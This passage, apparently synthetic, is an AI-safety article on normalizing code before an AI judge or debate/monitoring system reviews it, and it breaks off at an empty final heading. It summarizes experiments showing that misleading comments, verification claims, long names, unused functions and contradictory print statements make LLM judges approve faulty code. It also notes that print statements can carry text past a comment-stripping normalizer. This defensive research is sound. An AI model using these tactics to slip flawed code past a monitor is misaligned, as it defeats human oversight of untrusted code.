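# Canonicalizing code before a judge or monitor reads it

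## What it means to canonicalize code for a reader

Canonicalizing code means rewriting it into a standard form, so that versions of a program that differ only in comments, names or layout become identical. Programmers already do parts of this for other reasons. Formatters redo a file's layout, and minifiers remove comments and shorten names to make files smaller. In AI safety, canonicalization is meant to limit the author's influence on a person or language model deciding whether code is correct or harmful. An author who wants a particular answer can use comments, names and layout to push for it without changing what the program does.

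This situation comes up in AI debate and in monitoring. In debate, two AI systems (the debaters) argue opposite sides of a question, such as whether a function meets its specification. A judge, who may be a person or a model, decides whether the code, or a claim about it, is correct. A monitor is a person or model that reads code from an untrusted author to flag harmful behaviour. For example, a company that lets a capable but untrusted model write software might have a monitor read each submission before anything runs. In both cases, the most important error to avoid is a false negative, in which the reader accepts flawed or harmful code.

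### The machine and the other reader

Monperrus (2026) writes in *Knowledge as Code* that a program has two readers, a machine that executes it and a human who recovers its meaning. Prose has only a human reader. *NatGen* (2022) describes the same split as two channels. Compilers and interpreters use a formal channel with precise semantics, while people rely on a noisier natural channel of variable names and comments.

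A program's formal semantics already determine what it does, but people still need names and comments to understand it. *Do People Prefer "Natural" code?* (2019) explains why by imagining a reader who can always work out the meaning of code efficiently from its formal semantics. A developer could write for that reader in any style. Human readers need the developer's help, which means the developer can also mislead them. Language models share this weakness, at least in part. In *Don't Judge Code by Its Cover*, Moon, Hwang and colleagues (2025) found that comments and variable names affect models' judgments of whether code is correct, even when they don't change its behaviour.

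Which parts of the code the machine ignores depends on the language. Most of the examples here are in Python, where comments are "ignored by the syntax", according to *Lexical analysis* in the Python documentation. One exception is a comment in the first or second line of a file that declares the file's character encoding, which Python acts on. Indentation matters because it marks where a block begins and ends, but blank lines, spaces around operators and redundant parentheses do not.

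A docstring is a string at the start of a function, class or module that documents it. Readers treat it as a comment, but the Python documentation's *Glossary* notes that the compiler stores it in the `__doc__` attribute, where a running program can read it. Deleting a docstring is therefore harmless only if the program never reads `__doc__`.

Identifiers are the names a programmer chooses for variables, parameters, functions, classes and attributes. Shen, Xi and colleagues (2026), in *On the Lexical Superstition of Large Language Models for Code Comprehension*, distinguish two roles for an identifier. Its nominal role is to mark which occurrences refer to the same thing, and any unused name would do that equally well. Its descriptive role is to suggest to a reader what the thing is for. Consistent renaming keeps the nominal role and removes the descriptive one. Shen and colleagues limit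 renaming to names bound within the code, and they exclude programs in which a name affects how the program looks things up while running or how it interacts with anything outside it.

Here, a surface feature is a comment, name or layout choice that can change without changing what the program computes. A local variable's name usually qualifies, but the name of a function that other files call does not.

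### Parsing, renaming and printing

Most tools that canonicalize code first parse it into an abstract syntax tree (AST) instead of editing the text directly. The tree represents the program's structure without its layout and usually without its comments. For the line `sorted_values = list(values)`, Python builds an assignment node. Its target is a name node that holds the string `sorted_values`, and its value is a call node with `list` as the function and `values` as the argument. The grammar in Python's *ast* documentation has nodes for names, strings, loops and calls, but none for ordinary comments or blank lines. Nodes record their original line and column, but a printer that turns the tree back into code can ignore those positions and apply its own spacing.

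Canonicalization for a reader then takes three steps:

- Remove comments and docstrings. Parsing disposes of the comments. Docstrings survive it, because they are string expressions like any other, so the tool has to find them in the tree and delete them.
- Rename identifiers that are safe to rename, usually to a neutral series such as `v0`, `v1`, `v2`.
- Print the tree as text again, with one fixed layout.

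Barkhordar and Thapa (2026) built a pipeline of this kind for Python in *Style, Not Self*. They wanted to test whether language models recognize or favour their own code, so they needed a version of each program without the habits that identify the model that wrote it. Their tool also deletes type annotations. It doesn't change top-level function and class names (the tests call them), imported names, built-in functions, attributes or string literals. Error messages therefore stay the same, and so would anything an author chose to write in them.

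### Three properties of a normalizer

A normalizer is a program that carries out canonicalization, and its output for a given program is that program's normal form. Write N for the normalizer and x and y for source texts. Three properties define it:

- N is deterministic: the same x always gives the same N(x).
- N is idempotent: N(N(x)) = N(x), so applying it a second time changes nothing further.
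- If x and y differ only in the listed surface features, then N(x) = N(y).

The list in the last property is part of the definition. One normalizer's list may include only comments and layout, while another's also includes local names, so a statement that code "has been canonicalized" is incomplete without the list.

These conditions are easy to break by accident. Suppose a tool numbers the local variables in alphabetical order of their original names. Two programs that differ only in names can then get different numbering, which violates the last condition. Idempotence also fails once a function has more than ten locals. In alphabetical order `v10` comes before `v2`, so a second pass renames `v10` to `v2`, `v2` to `v3`, and so on. Numbering the variables by first appearance avoids both faults.

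The three properties do not require a normalizer to preserve a program's behaviour. A normalizer that returns an empty file for every input is deterministic and idempotent, and gives the same output for programs that differ only in their comments, but it is useless to a judge. A normalizer for this purpose must therefore also be semantics-preserving, meaning that the program it rewrites behaves the same as the original on every input, under a stated notion of behaviour.

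The word "stated" is needed because people mean different things by "behaviour". Shen and colleagues use "functionality" for the mapping from inputs to outputs, including effects on anything outside the program. Their own criterion is stricter because it also requires the control flow, data flow, operations and literals to stay the same. Correctly renaming local variables meets this criterion, but replacing a sorting routine with one that uses a different algorithm does not, even though the functionality is the same.

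N must always preserve behaviour, because otherwise the judge would be ruling on code that nobody will run. Ideally, N would also give the same output for any two programs that behave alike, which would leave an author no choice in how the code looks to the judge. No algorithm can meet both requirements for all programs in a general-purpose language, but merging only some equivalent programs is still useful. A normalizer that merges only versions differing in comments, local names and spacing already prevents an author from using those three to persuade the judge.

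Barkhordar and Thapa compared pairs of solutions that two different models had written for the same task in MBPP, a benchmark of short Python problems. Before normalization, at most 2% of the pairs were identical. Afterwards, 7–11% were identical in pairings that involved GPT-5, and 26–33% in three pairings of other models. The remaining pairs still differed, presumably mostly because the models had organized the computation differently, which the normalizer should not change.

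### A median function that does not sort

The median of a list is its middle value when the list is sorted. Here is a faulty Python function for computing it, presented the way a debater might if they wanted the judge to accept it.

```python
def median(values):
    """Return the median of a non-empty list of numbers.

    Verified against the reference implementation.
    """
    # sort a copy, so that the caller's list stays as it was
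    sorted_values = list(values)

    n   = len(sorted_values)
    mid = n // 2
    if (n % 2) == 1:
        return sorted_values[mid]
    return (sorted_values[mid - 1] + sorted_values[mid]) / 2
```

The call `list(values)` copies the list without sorting it. Given [3, 1, 2], the function computes the middle position (position 1, since Python counts from 0) and returns the value there, which is 1, but the correct answer is 2. The function returns the right answer for [1, 2, 3] because that list is already sorted, so a judge who tries only one sorted example will see nothing wrong.

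The presentation covers the fault three times over. The docstring contains a claim of verification, the comment describes a sort, and the variable name repeats the claim wherever it occurs. Removing the docstring and the comment is not enough, since `sorted_values` still stands in five places, including the very expressions where the order of the list matters. Renaming the parameter and the locals deals with that, and printing from the tree removes the blank lines, the aligned equals signs and the unneeded parentheses:

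```python
def median(v0):
    v1 = list(v0)
    v2 = len(v1)
    v3 = v2 // 2
    if v2 % 2 == 1:
        return v1[v3]
    return (v1[v3 - 1] + v1[v3]) / 2
```

This version still returns 1 for [3, 1, 2] because it doesn't sort its input, but the false claims are gone and nothing in its seven lines suggests that it does. A correct function written the same way would differ only in its second line, which would be `v1 = sorted(v0)` instead of `v1 = list(v0)`. That difference remains because `list` and `sorted` are built-in names, which the normalizer must not change. The name `median` also remains, and the judge needs either that name or a separate task description to know what the function should return.

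A debater who had named the variable `data` and written no comments would have produced the same normal form. But a correct function that copies the list and calls `.sort()` on the copy gets a different normal form from the one that uses `sorted`, although both return the same medians. This is the partial merging described above, and it doesn't harm the judge.

A rewriting tool would do harm if it detected the mismatch and replaced `list` with `sorted`. The judge would then read a correct function and approve it while the machine kept running the faulty one, so the safeguard itself would have caused a false negative.

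Even a faithful rewrite removes useful information. An alert judge could have noticed that the comment "sort a copy" disagrees with the line below it. Deleting the comment keeps it from misleading the judge, but also removes that clue. Canonicalization deletes accurate comments too. In Barkhordar and Thapa's before-and-after example, a function checks whether all the tuples in a collection have the same length, and a comment explains that an empty collection counts as equal by default. After normalization, an early `return True` remains, and the reader has to guess whether it is intentional.

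### Behaviour, influence and judgement

Each step of the rewriting therefore raises three separate questions: whether it preserves the program's behaviour, whether it removes the influence on the reader, and whether it helps the reader judge better. A yes to one does not imply a yes to the others.

Barkhordar and Thapa reran the benchmark tests on the normalized solutions of five models. Every solution that had passed before still passed, and the failures did not change. This is good evidence that normalization preserves behaviour, but it is not proof, because tests cover only the inputs that someone thought to include. Normalizers can also have implementation errors. An earlier version of theirs broke imports inside function bodies, and they had to fix it and repeat the affected judgments.

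In a test of influence, models chose the better of two solutions without being told who wrote them. Claude Haiku 4.5 picked its own code over DeepSeek-V3's 75.2% of the time, while Gemini 2.5 Flash, a neutral judge of the same items, picked Claude's 63.4% of the time. On normalized code the figures were 47.8% and 48.9%, so Claude no longer favored its own code more than the neutral judge did. Much of the original excess came from a preference for documented code. Normalization did not remove every influence, however. When Claude Haiku had to identify its own solution from a normalized pair in which GPT-5 had written the other, it still tended to choose the longer one, and its accuracy was 35.3%, compared with 50% for guessing.

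Whether the reader judges better is the hardest of the three questions to answer and the one that matters for safety. A judge that no longer favours its own code, or is no longer misled by comments, may still miss that `list` does not sort. It may even do worse if the removed names and comments were mostly true and it had relied on them to follow the program. Testing this requires giving judges correct and faulty programs in both original and canonical form, then counting how often they reject correct code and accept faulty code. The solutions in Barkhordar and Thapa's experiment averaged 7–20 lines, and a monitor usually has to read far more.

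## What a normal form guarantees and what it costs

A judge that reads only normal forms gives the same verdict on every version of a program that the normalizer converts to the same form. This consistency can reduce accuracy, because the comments and names that normalization removes sometimes carry true information about the code. *Robust and Accurate Authorship Attribution via Program Normalization* (Wang, Alhanahnah and colleagues, 2020) analyzes both effects for a different task, identifying the programmer who wrote a piece of code. Its method, normalize-and-predict, converts every program to its normal form, then trains and runs a classifier only on normal forms. A classifier is any function that assigns an input one of a fixed set of labels, so a judge that answers "correct" or "faulty" is also a classifier.

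### Rewrites as a graph

The framework starts from a list of rewrites that an attacker may apply any number of times and in any order. The list defines a relation R, the set of all pairs (x, z) such that one rewrite turns text x into text z. A classifier is robust at x if it gives the same label to x and to every text the attacker can reach from x.

The pairs in R form a graph, with a point for every program text and an arrow from x to z for every pair (x, z). If we ignore the direction of the arrows, the graph splits into separate pieces called connected components. If the list includes comments, local names and spacing, the commented and uncommented versions of the faulty `median` function belong to one component, and the correct function that calls `sorted` belongs to another.

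A classifier is robust on a whole component exactly when it gives every member the same label. Rewrites never lead out of a component, so if all its members share a label, no rewrite can change the answer. Conversely, if two members get different labels, then somewhere along the chain of rewrites connecting them, two neighbours must get different labels. An attacker can then change the answer with a single rewrite from at least one of those neighbours.

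A normalizer achieves robustness by mapping every member of a component to one chosen member. The classifier then receives the same text for all of them, so its output can't differ between them. This holds for any classifier, even if the attacker knows exactly how the classifier and the normalizer work. Because the chosen text comes from the same component as the original, it also behaves the same way, provided every rewrite on the list preserves behaviour.

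The proof treats the classifier as a fixed function of the text. A language model that samples its answers may give different verdicts on the same text, so the guarantee then covers only the probability of each verdict. The guarantee no longer holds if the judge sees anything else the author wrote, such as the original file.

### The price in accuracy

Let μ(x) be the probability that a submission is x, and let η(x, l) be the probability that the right label for x is l. (The 2020 paper prints the definition of η with "y ≠ l", but its formula needs the probability that y = l.) A robust classifier must choose one label for each component C, and the best choice is the label that is right most often there. Its accuracy is then

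Σ over components C of [ max over labels l of Σ over x in C of μ(x) η(x, l) ].

For example, a judge that cannot completely follow a long function might rely partly on whether it has careful comments. Suppose commented functions (x) make up 30% of all submissions and are correct 90% of the time, while functions of the same kind without comments (z) make up 20% and are correct 20% of the time.

If the judge can treat x and z differently, its best policy is to accept x and reject z. Measured as shares of all submissions, it is then right on 0.3 × 0.9 = 0.27 from the first group and 0.2 × 0.8 = 0.16 from the second, or 0.43 in total. If the normalizer deletes the comments, the judge must give both groups the same answer. Accepting both is right on 0.27 + 0.04 = 0.31, and rejecting both on 0.03 + 0.16 = 0.19. Deleting the comments therefore lowers the best total from 0.43 to 0.31, a loss of 0.12,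 because the comments carried information.

Even when the rewrite between x and z preserves behaviour, the two can differ in how often they are correct. Wang and colleagues explain this with malware detectors that use only certain features of a program. Some file-compression tools may match ransomware on those features. If the tools' developers agree to mark their programs with a harmless pattern, the pattern becomes good evidence that a program is safe, until ransomware developers copy it.

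When a reader is judging correctness, how much normalization loses depends on how well the reader can work out what the code does. A program is correct if its behaviour meets the specification, so all versions of one program have the same true label, and a reader who could always work out the behaviour would lose nothing. A limited reader cannot tell some different programs apart and guesses between them from surface features, so it can lose useful evidence when those features are removed. When the question is who wrote the code, even an ideal reader loses evidence, because behaviour does not determine authorship and the normalizer removes the author's habits.

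The 0.43 also depends on authors not reacting to the judge. Suppose everyone with a faulty uncommented function adds careful comments, while nobody with a correct function changes anything. The judge who trusts comments is then right on only 0.27 of all submissions, less than the merged judge's 0.31. The share of submissions that are faulty and accepted rises from 0.03 to 0.19.

However, the merged judge also accepts the faulty 0.19, because accepting everything in the component maximizes accuracy. Accuracy counts both kinds of error equally, which is wrong for a monitor, where false negatives matter most. If accepting a faulty function is more than about 1.6 times as bad as rejecting a correct one (0.31 divided by 0.19), it is better to reject everything in the component. In both cases, the normalizer makes the judge consistent but doesn't help it separate good code from bad.

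Adding a rewrite to the list can never raise the best robust accuracy. It lowers that accuracy if it joins components whose most likely labels differ, and otherwise has no effect. This is a reason to normalize only the features an author can exploit.

Merging texts can lower the best achievable accuracy when some rewrites work in only one direction. Suppose x can become either z₁ or z₂, but neither can change back, and the three have different correct labels. If x makes up 2% of inputs and the others 49% each, a classifier that labels z₁ and z₂ correctly is right on 98% whatever the attacker does. Merging all three gives them the same label, which limits accuracy to 49%. A later version of the work, *Robust Learning against Relational Adversaries* (2022), avoids this by merging only texts that the attacker can turn into each other. Wang and colleagues prove that this does not reduce the best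 accuracy achievable against the attacker. Changes to comments, local names and layout are all reversible, so the result applies to them. Any accuracy that normalization loses on honest submissions is accuracy that an attacker with the same rewrites could have taken away anyway.

These results describe the best possible classifier, and a simpler one may even gain from normalization. Wang and colleagues construct an example with five yes-or-no features, two of them interchangeable. No linear classifier, which adds up weighted features and compares the total with a threshold, can label every input correctly from the original features, but one can once the interchangeable pair is merged.

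### Tests on authorship and malware

Wang and colleagues tested the method on 1,632 C++ files from the programming contest Google Code Jam, written by 204 authors who had each solved the same eight problems. They tested on each problem in turn after training on the other seven. Their two models were a random forest, which combines the votes of many decision trees, and an LSTM, a neural network that processes sequences. The attack searches through combinations of 42 rewrites, such as turning a `for` loop into a `while` loop, until the model misidentifies the author.

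Finding the exact normal form by exploring a component is too slow, because the component can grow exponentially with the number of rewrites. The researchers' normalizer instead counts 16 features, such as `for` loops and C-style input and output calls, and applies rewrites that lower the total until no rewrite lowers it further. It covers 35 of the 42 rewrites. The researchers left function and variable names unchanged because normalizing them could hide too much of the evidence about who wrote the code.

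The 2022 version reports these accuracies, in percent:

| Attack | Forest, original code | Forest, normal forms | LSTM, original code | LSTM, normal forms | LSTM, adversarial training |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 90.4 | 76.1 | 88.4 | 78.7 | 76.7 |
| 35 rewrites, normalizer unknown to attacker | 13.2 | 72.3 | 21.1 | 73.7 | 30.8 |
| 35 rewrites, normalizer known | 13.2 | 70.5 | 21.1 | 71.2 | 30.8 |
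| All 42 rewrites, normalizer known | 1.0 | 37.3 | 0.9 | 49.9 | 25.2 |

Without an attack, normalization cost the forest 14.3 percentage points and the LSTM 9.7. Under attack, it kept both models above 70% as long as the attacker used only the 35 covered rewrites. An exact normalizer would have made the first two rows equal, so the gaps of 3.8 and 5.0 points indicate that the shortcut left some versions unmerged. Once the attacker could use the other seven rewrites, accuracy fell to 37.3% and 49.9%, because the guarantee does not extend beyond the list. (The 2020 version gives the same two figures for an attack that used only those seven.)

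The last column shows the usual alternative, adversarial training, in which the model learns from attacked examples. It took more than 20 days, even though the researchers weakened the attack during training to save time. Normalizing the data took less than 12 hours.

Some of the 35 rewrites would be unsafe to apply before a judge reads the code. One replaces every C++ integer type with `long long`, which can hold larger numbers. A function that fails because a sum is too large for an `int` may work after that change, and the judge would then approve it even though the original code fails when it runs. This hardly matters for attribution, since the classifier only has to identify an author.

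The second experiment in the 2022 paper is closer to monitoring. It represented malicious and benign Windows programs by which of 22,761 API calls (requests to the operating system and its libraries) each program used. An attacker could replace a call with an equivalent one or add calls that did nothing useful. Wang and colleagues merged the equivalent calls within each of nearly 2,000 groups, and used adversarial training to defend against added calls.

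The resulting detector missed 5.0% of malware without an attack and 5.5% with one. With adversarial training alone, the miss rates were 5.8% and 27.9%, and with no defence they were 6.2% and 100%. The combined defence raised false alarms on benign programs from 10.0% to 11.9%, a small increase given the malware it caught. However, someone writing a program has far more choices than which of several equivalent calls to use.

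### A judge that nobody has retrained

In all of these experiments, the researchers trained the defended classifiers on normal forms. An off-the-shelf language model has learned mostly from ordinary code, with its names and comments, and people who use one as a judge usually put the normalized program in the prompt without training the model on normal forms. The proof of consistency still holds because it applies to any classifier, but the accuracy formula doesn't, because it assumes that the classifier has learned the best label for each component. In the worked example, a judge that misreads the unfamiliar code might consistently reject both groups and be right on 0.19 of submissions instead of 0.31.

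*I still know it's you! On Challenges in Anonymizing Source Code* (Horlboge, Quiring and colleagues, 2022) measured how accurately classifiers trained on code that hadn't been normalized could identify who wrote normalized code. The researchers wanted to protect programmers from identification, so a drop in accuracy was a success. They first removed comments and layout differences from 240 C files by 30 authors. Their normalizer then replaced variable and function names, reduced the variety of data types and simplified control structures. Two models trained on files that had gone through only the first step identified the author 68.8% and 75.4% of the time on such files, and 20.4% and 14.6% of the time on normalized files.

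When the researchers added normalized files to the training data, accuracy recovered to about 53% for both models, but that test mixed original and normalized files in equal numbers. If accuracy on the original files did not change, the models were right on about 38% and 30% of the normalized ones. On that assumption, part of the initial drop came from unfamiliarity, which retraining could fix. The rest came from evidence that the normalizer had removed or that the models still could not use.

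These figures do not predict how much accuracy a code judge would lose. Names are much better evidence of who wrote a program than of whether it is correct, and a large language model is trained on far more varied code than a classifier that learns from a few hundred files. But the problem is of the same kind, and researchers have measured accuracy losses in language models from renaming alone. A company that trains its own monitor could include normal forms in the training data, which would bring the monitor closer to the setting that Wang and colleagues analysed.

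### Why some equivalent programs stay apart

A longer list of rewrites merges more programs, but no algorithm can give all equivalent programs in a general-purpose language the same normal form. Suppose an algorithm N preserved behaviour and gave any two equivalent programs the same output. Comparing N's outputs on programs x and y would then show whether they were equivalent. Equal outputs would mean that x and y both behaved like the same third program, and different outputs would mean that they were not equivalent. But no algorithm can decide equivalence for every pair of programs in such a language.

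Such a test would settle questions that no algorithm can settle. Let `p` be any program that takes no input, and let `halts_within(p, n)` run it for `n` steps and report whether it has finished. Compare these two functions, where `n` is any non-negative whole number:

```python
def f(n):
    return 1 if halts_within(p, n) else 0

def g(n):
    return 0
```

Both functions always return an answer, and they agree for every `n` exactly when `p` never finishes. An equivalence test could therefore determine whether any given program runs forever. This is the halting problem, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm answers it correctly in every case. Rice's theorem extends the result to every property of a program's behaviour that some programs have and others lack, such as returning 0 for every input.

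Horlboge and colleagues reached the same limit while studying author anonymity. They wanted a rewrite whose output no possible method could use to tell authors apart. If two equivalent programs by different authors still differed after the rewrite, someone could build a method that looked for that difference. The rewrite would therefore have to make all equivalent programs identical, which is impossible in general. The same argument applies to judges. Any normalizer leaves some equivalent programs with different normal forms, and some conceivable judge would treat them differently. A particular judge may not be affected by those differences, so it is still worth measuring which ones change its output.

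The obstacle is weaker for finite Boolean circuits, which compute with AND, OR and NOT gates on a fixed number of input bits and have no loops. Trying every input shows whether two circuits are equivalent, so a full canonical form exists. A program can find it by going through all circuits of the same size in a fixed order and returning the first that computes the same function. *Exact Non-Identity Check and Gate-Teleportation-Based Indistinguishability Obfuscation are NP-hard* (2025) describes this construction as an inefficient indistinguishability obfuscator. An obfuscator rewrites a circuit to hide how its author built it, and this kind must make equivalent circuits of equal size impossible to tell apart. The construction meets this requirement perfectly because it returns the same circuit for all of them.

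Comparing two functions by testing every input is infeasible at realistic sizes. A function of two 32-bit integers has 2⁶⁴ possible inputs, so a single comparison would take about 585 years at a billion tests per second. Nobody knows an efficient alternative, and there is strong evidence that none exists. A circuit that outputs 0 on every input would have the same canonical form as a trivial circuit of equal size that always outputs 0, so an efficient way to compute canonical forms would quickly decide whether any input makes a given circuit output 1. That problem is NP-complete, so solving it efficiently would prove P = NP, which most computer scientists believe is false.

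Allowing some randomness does not seem to help. According to *Partial-indistinguishability obfuscation using braids* (2012), an efficient obfuscator whose outputs for equivalent circuits had almost the same distribution would collapse the polynomial hierarchy, a sequence of complexity classes built on NP, to its second level. Complexity theorists consider such a collapse unlikely too.

Even an efficient canonical form might be a poor choice to show a judge. If the form is the first suitable circuit in a list, it keeps none of the original author's choices, including those that made the code easy to follow. In practice, a tool can prove many particular pairs of programs equivalent, and a normalizer can convert the versions its developer knows how to handle into the same form.

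## How comments, names and padding change an LLM judge's verdict

Deleting comments and renaming variables can make a judge less accurate on honest code, so it is worth doing only if comments and variable names sway the judge. Moon and colleagues measured this effect in language models that decide whether code is correct. Other researchers have measured how similar changes affect models that predict a program's output or revise code after a review.

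### Six changes to 2,000 programs

Moon and colleagues took 200 problems for each of five languages (C++, Python, Java, JavaScript and Go) from a programming contest for beginners. For each problem they picked one correct and one incorrect solution that people had submitted. The incorrect solutions compiled and ran but gave wrong answers, so a judge had to follow the logic to reject them. The researchers deleted all the original comments and then made six altered versions of each program:

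- A comment at the top says "correct code".
- A comment says that an expert wrote the program.
- A comment says that a beginner wrote it.
- Two or three comments, which a language model wrote, misdescribe what the code does.
- Strings of 24 random letters replace the names of variables and parameters.
- An extra function appears at the top, and the program never calls it.

The six main judges were GPT-4o, GPT-4o-mini, Gemini 2.0 Flash, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, and the 70B and 8B versions of LLaMA 3.1. The published version adds two CodeLLaMA models, which specialize in code. Each judge received the task description and the program, but no tests or reference solution, and reasoned step by step before giving its verdict.

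### Why one accuracy figure is not enough

A judge's accuracy on correct programs is the share it approves, and its accuracy on incorrect programs is the share it rejects. Anything that makes the judge more lenient raises the first and lowers the second, so their average can stay almost the same even when both change a lot.

For GPT-4o on Python, the "correct code" comment raised accuracy on correct programs from 84.7% to 92.2% and lowered accuracy on incorrect ones from 63.1% to 51.0%, so the average fell only from 73.9% to 71.6%. Comments that misdescribed the code lowered the average to 71.5%, but by making the judge much stricter. GPT-4o approved 49.0% of the faulty programs with the "correct code" comment and 17.5% with the inaccurate descriptions.

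The table below shows approval rates for Python. The first number in each cell is the percentage of correct programs the judge approved, and the second is the percentage of faulty programs it approved (its false negatives).

| Change | GPT-4o | Gemini 2.0 Flash | Claude 3.5 Sonnet | LLaMA 3.1 70B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 84.7 / 36.9 | 79.7 / 36.5 | 64.2 / 19.3 | 49.0 / 16.5 |
| "Correct code" | 92.2 / 49.0 | 88.1 / 48.2 | 82.8 / 34.7 | 83.3 / 41.9 |
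| Expert author | 84.6 / 39.2 | 81.3 / 39.8 | 63.2 / 18.7 | 46.2 / 16.5 |
| Beginner author | 79.6 / 29.0 | 76.0 / 32.2 | 53.2 / 13.2 | 49.5 / 15.1 |
| Misdescribed task | 60.5 / 17.5 | 68.8 / 23.5 | 48.7 / 14.5 | 24.5 / 7.0 |
| Random 24-letter names | 87.3 / 44.6 | 84.3 / 48.2 | 73.0 / 31.0 | 50.0 / 18.1 |
| One unused function | 77.7 / 32.8 | 81.6 / 43.2 | 60.7 / 19.8 | 44.4 / 17.2 |

The "correct code" comment raised LLaMA 3.1 70B's average accuracy from 66.3% to 70.7%. The model had been rejecting half of the correct programs, and the comment made it less strict. But the model also approved two and a half times as many faulty programs, which average accuracy alone doesn't show.

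In most cells, a change moves the approval rates for correct and faulty code in the same direction. The comments mainly affect how readily the judge approves code, and have less effect on how well it separates correct from faulty code. With the "correct code" comment on every program, GPT-4o approved correct programs 43 percentage points more often than faulty ones, compared with 48 points without it.

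If only the faulty programs contained the comment, however, LLaMA would approve 49.0% of the correct programs and 41.9% of the faulty ones, which would make its verdict almost worthless. GPT-4o would approve 84.7% and 49.0%, respectively.

Claiming to be an expert had little effect, but claiming to be a beginner lowered approval in nearly all cases, including by 18.8 points for Claude 3.5 Sonnet on correct JavaScript programs. Comments that misdescribed the task lowered accuracy on correct code the most. GPT-4o's accuracy on correct Java programs fell by 26.7 points, from 86.5% to 59.8%, and LLaMA 3.1 70B's fell by 29.7, from 54.8% to 25.1%. Larger models were no more robust to these comments. Averaged over correct and incorrect programs in all the languages, the comments shifted GPT-4o's accuracy by 20.8 points and GPT-4o-mini's by 16.1.

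An author who wants faulty code approved would not use comments like these, because they make the judge suspicious. That suspicion can instead hurt honest authors whose comments are out of date. The comment in the faulty `median` function is false in a different way, because it describes a step that the task requires but the code omits. None of the six changes tests that kind of comment, which could well be more persuasive than a bare "correct code".

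The baseline programs contain no comments, so the first row of the table also shows what would happen if a normalizer deleted the added ones. GPT-4o would still approve 36.9% of the faulty Python programs, down from 49.0%. The experiment cannot show how deleting true comments would affect a judge, because the researchers removed those before they started. On a different task, security review, an experiment found that comments had no clear effect (see the next section).

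### Longer names and more unused functions

Random names made all four judges in the table more likely to approve faulty Python programs. This is surprising, because meaningless names should make code harder to follow. One possible reason is that renaming can also make the code longer. In the paper's illustration, the loop variable `i` becomes `qkzlpbsidmsm`.

Moon and colleagues replaced the names in Python programs with random ones of 1, 2, 8, 12, 16, 24 or 48 letters and had Gemini 2.0 Flash judge the results. With one-letter names, the judge approved fewer programs than with the original names. With names of two or more letters, it approved more of both the correct and the faulty programs, and the effect grew with name length. At 24 letters, it approved 48.2% of the faulty programs, the same share as with the "correct code" comment. The researchers suggest that longer names may look more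 sophisticated to a model, but they did not test this.

This matters when choosing neutral names for a normal form. A name such as `v0` is two characters long but not random, so the experiment does not show how a judge would react to it. A naming scheme could make a judge more lenient or stricter with every author. Anyone using one should therefore measure the judge's false negative rate on normal forms rather than assume it matches the rate on ordinary code.

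A single unused function had no consistent effect across judges. GPT-4o approved fewer Python programs with one, while Gemini approved more. But when the researchers added more of them for Gemini, the direction became clear:

| Unused functions | Correct programs approved (%) | Faulty programs approved (%) |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 79.7 | 36.5 |
| 1 | 81.6 | 43.2 |
| 2 | 82.8 | 39.7 |
| 4 | 85.0 | 50.3 |
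| 6 | 88.2 | 55.1 |
| 8 | 89.3 | 53.4 |

The padding came from correct solutions to other contest problems. Eight extra functions made the programs more than five times their original length, so most of what the judge read was correct code unrelated to the task. Approval of faulty code rose by 17 points and approval of correct code by 10, so the judge became more lenient and worse at separating the two. The researchers acknowledge that the test cannot distinguish the effect of length from that of apparent complexity. These results, like those for name length, come from one model and one language.

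### Asking the judge to write tests first

A judge that has to check code against specific inputs might pay less attention to how the code looks. Moon and colleagues therefore asked Gemini 2.0 Flash to write test cases and use them to assess each Python program. With this method, the average shift fell from 8.4 points to 4.1 on faulty programs, but only from 5.2 to 4.2 on correct ones.

The protection worked mostly against comments that made the judge stricter. The comment that misdescribed the task now lowered approval of correct code by 3.3 points instead of 10.8. The "correct code" comment still raised approval of correct programs by 8.1 points, about as much as before, and approval of faulty ones by 6.7, down from 11.7.

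When programs had no added cue, the method lowered accuracy on correct programs from 79.7% to 63.8% and raised accuracy on faulty ones from 63.5% to 69.7%. This might be acceptable in a monitor because it reduces false negatives, but average accuracy fell from 71.6% to about 67%.

### Predicting what code returns

To decide whether a program meets its specification, a judge needs some idea of what the program does. In *CodeCrash*, Lam, Wang and colleagues (2025) tested this skill separately by asking 17 language models what a Python function would return for a given input. Of the 1,279 questions, 800 came from CRUXEval, a set of short model-generated functions, and 479 came from LiveCodeBench, which uses solutions that people had submitted to the programming site LeetCode.

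When the models answered directly, misleading text and structural changes reduced their accuracy by an average of 23.2% of its original value. A model that was right on 60% of the questions would fall to about 46%. When the models reasoned step by step, the average loss was 13.8%.

An earlier version of the study, *CODECRASH* by Lam, Huang and colleagues (2025), breaks the losses down by type of change. Its baseline was already partly canonical, because the researchers had parsed and reprinted every function. These are the average losses from that baseline for direct answers, in percentage points:

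| Change | CRUXEval | LiveCodeBench |
|---|---|---|
| Neutral names for functions, parameters and variables | 2.4 | 8.2 |
| Conditions in a more roundabout but equivalent form | 1.5 | 1.9 |
| Added code that does not affect the result | 8.0 | 3.9 |
| All three of these together | 13.2 | 15.5 |
| Comments that contradict the code | 12.0 | 16.0 |
| Print statements that contradict the code | 12.3 | 15.0 |
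| A comment with a plausible but false hint about the result | 7.1 | 17.8 |

The first row compares meaningful names with neutral ones such as `Var_0`, so it measures one way canonicalization itself can lower scores. The drop is small on CRUXEval, where every function already had the uninformative name `f`. On LiveCodeBench, Claude 3.5 Sonnet lost 16.8 points and DeepSeek-V3 lost 16.4. A normalizer that keeps top-level function names would presumably cause a smaller drop.

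Print statements did almost as much harm as comments. A normalizer that deletes comments leaves print statements in place, and deleting those too would normally change the program's behaviour. An author who knows that a normalizer will strip comments can therefore use a print statement for the text they would have put in a comment. The code may print something odd when it runs, but only after the judge has read it.

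The misleading text did less harm when models had to find an input that would produce a given output. On that task, contradictory comments and print statements slightly raised average accuracy for direct answers. Lam and colleagues found that the false messages led models to skip parts of the code, but the models could still reach an acceptable answer because several inputs are often valid. False hints about the result still lowered accuracy, by a relative 20% on average.

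Removing comments before a model reads the code is more reliable than telling the model to ignore them. On LiveCodeBench, Lam and colleagues tested an explicit instruction to ignore comments and other non-code elements. When DeepSeek-V3 answered directly, contradictory comments reduced its accuracy from 67.8% to 39.7%, and the instruction raised it only to 41.8%. With step-by-step reasoning, the instruction raised DeepSeek-V3's accuracy from 70.2% to 82.1%, compared with 92.1% without the comments, and GPT-4o's from 87.5% to 89.4%, compared with 94.4%.

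### Reasoning models and false hints

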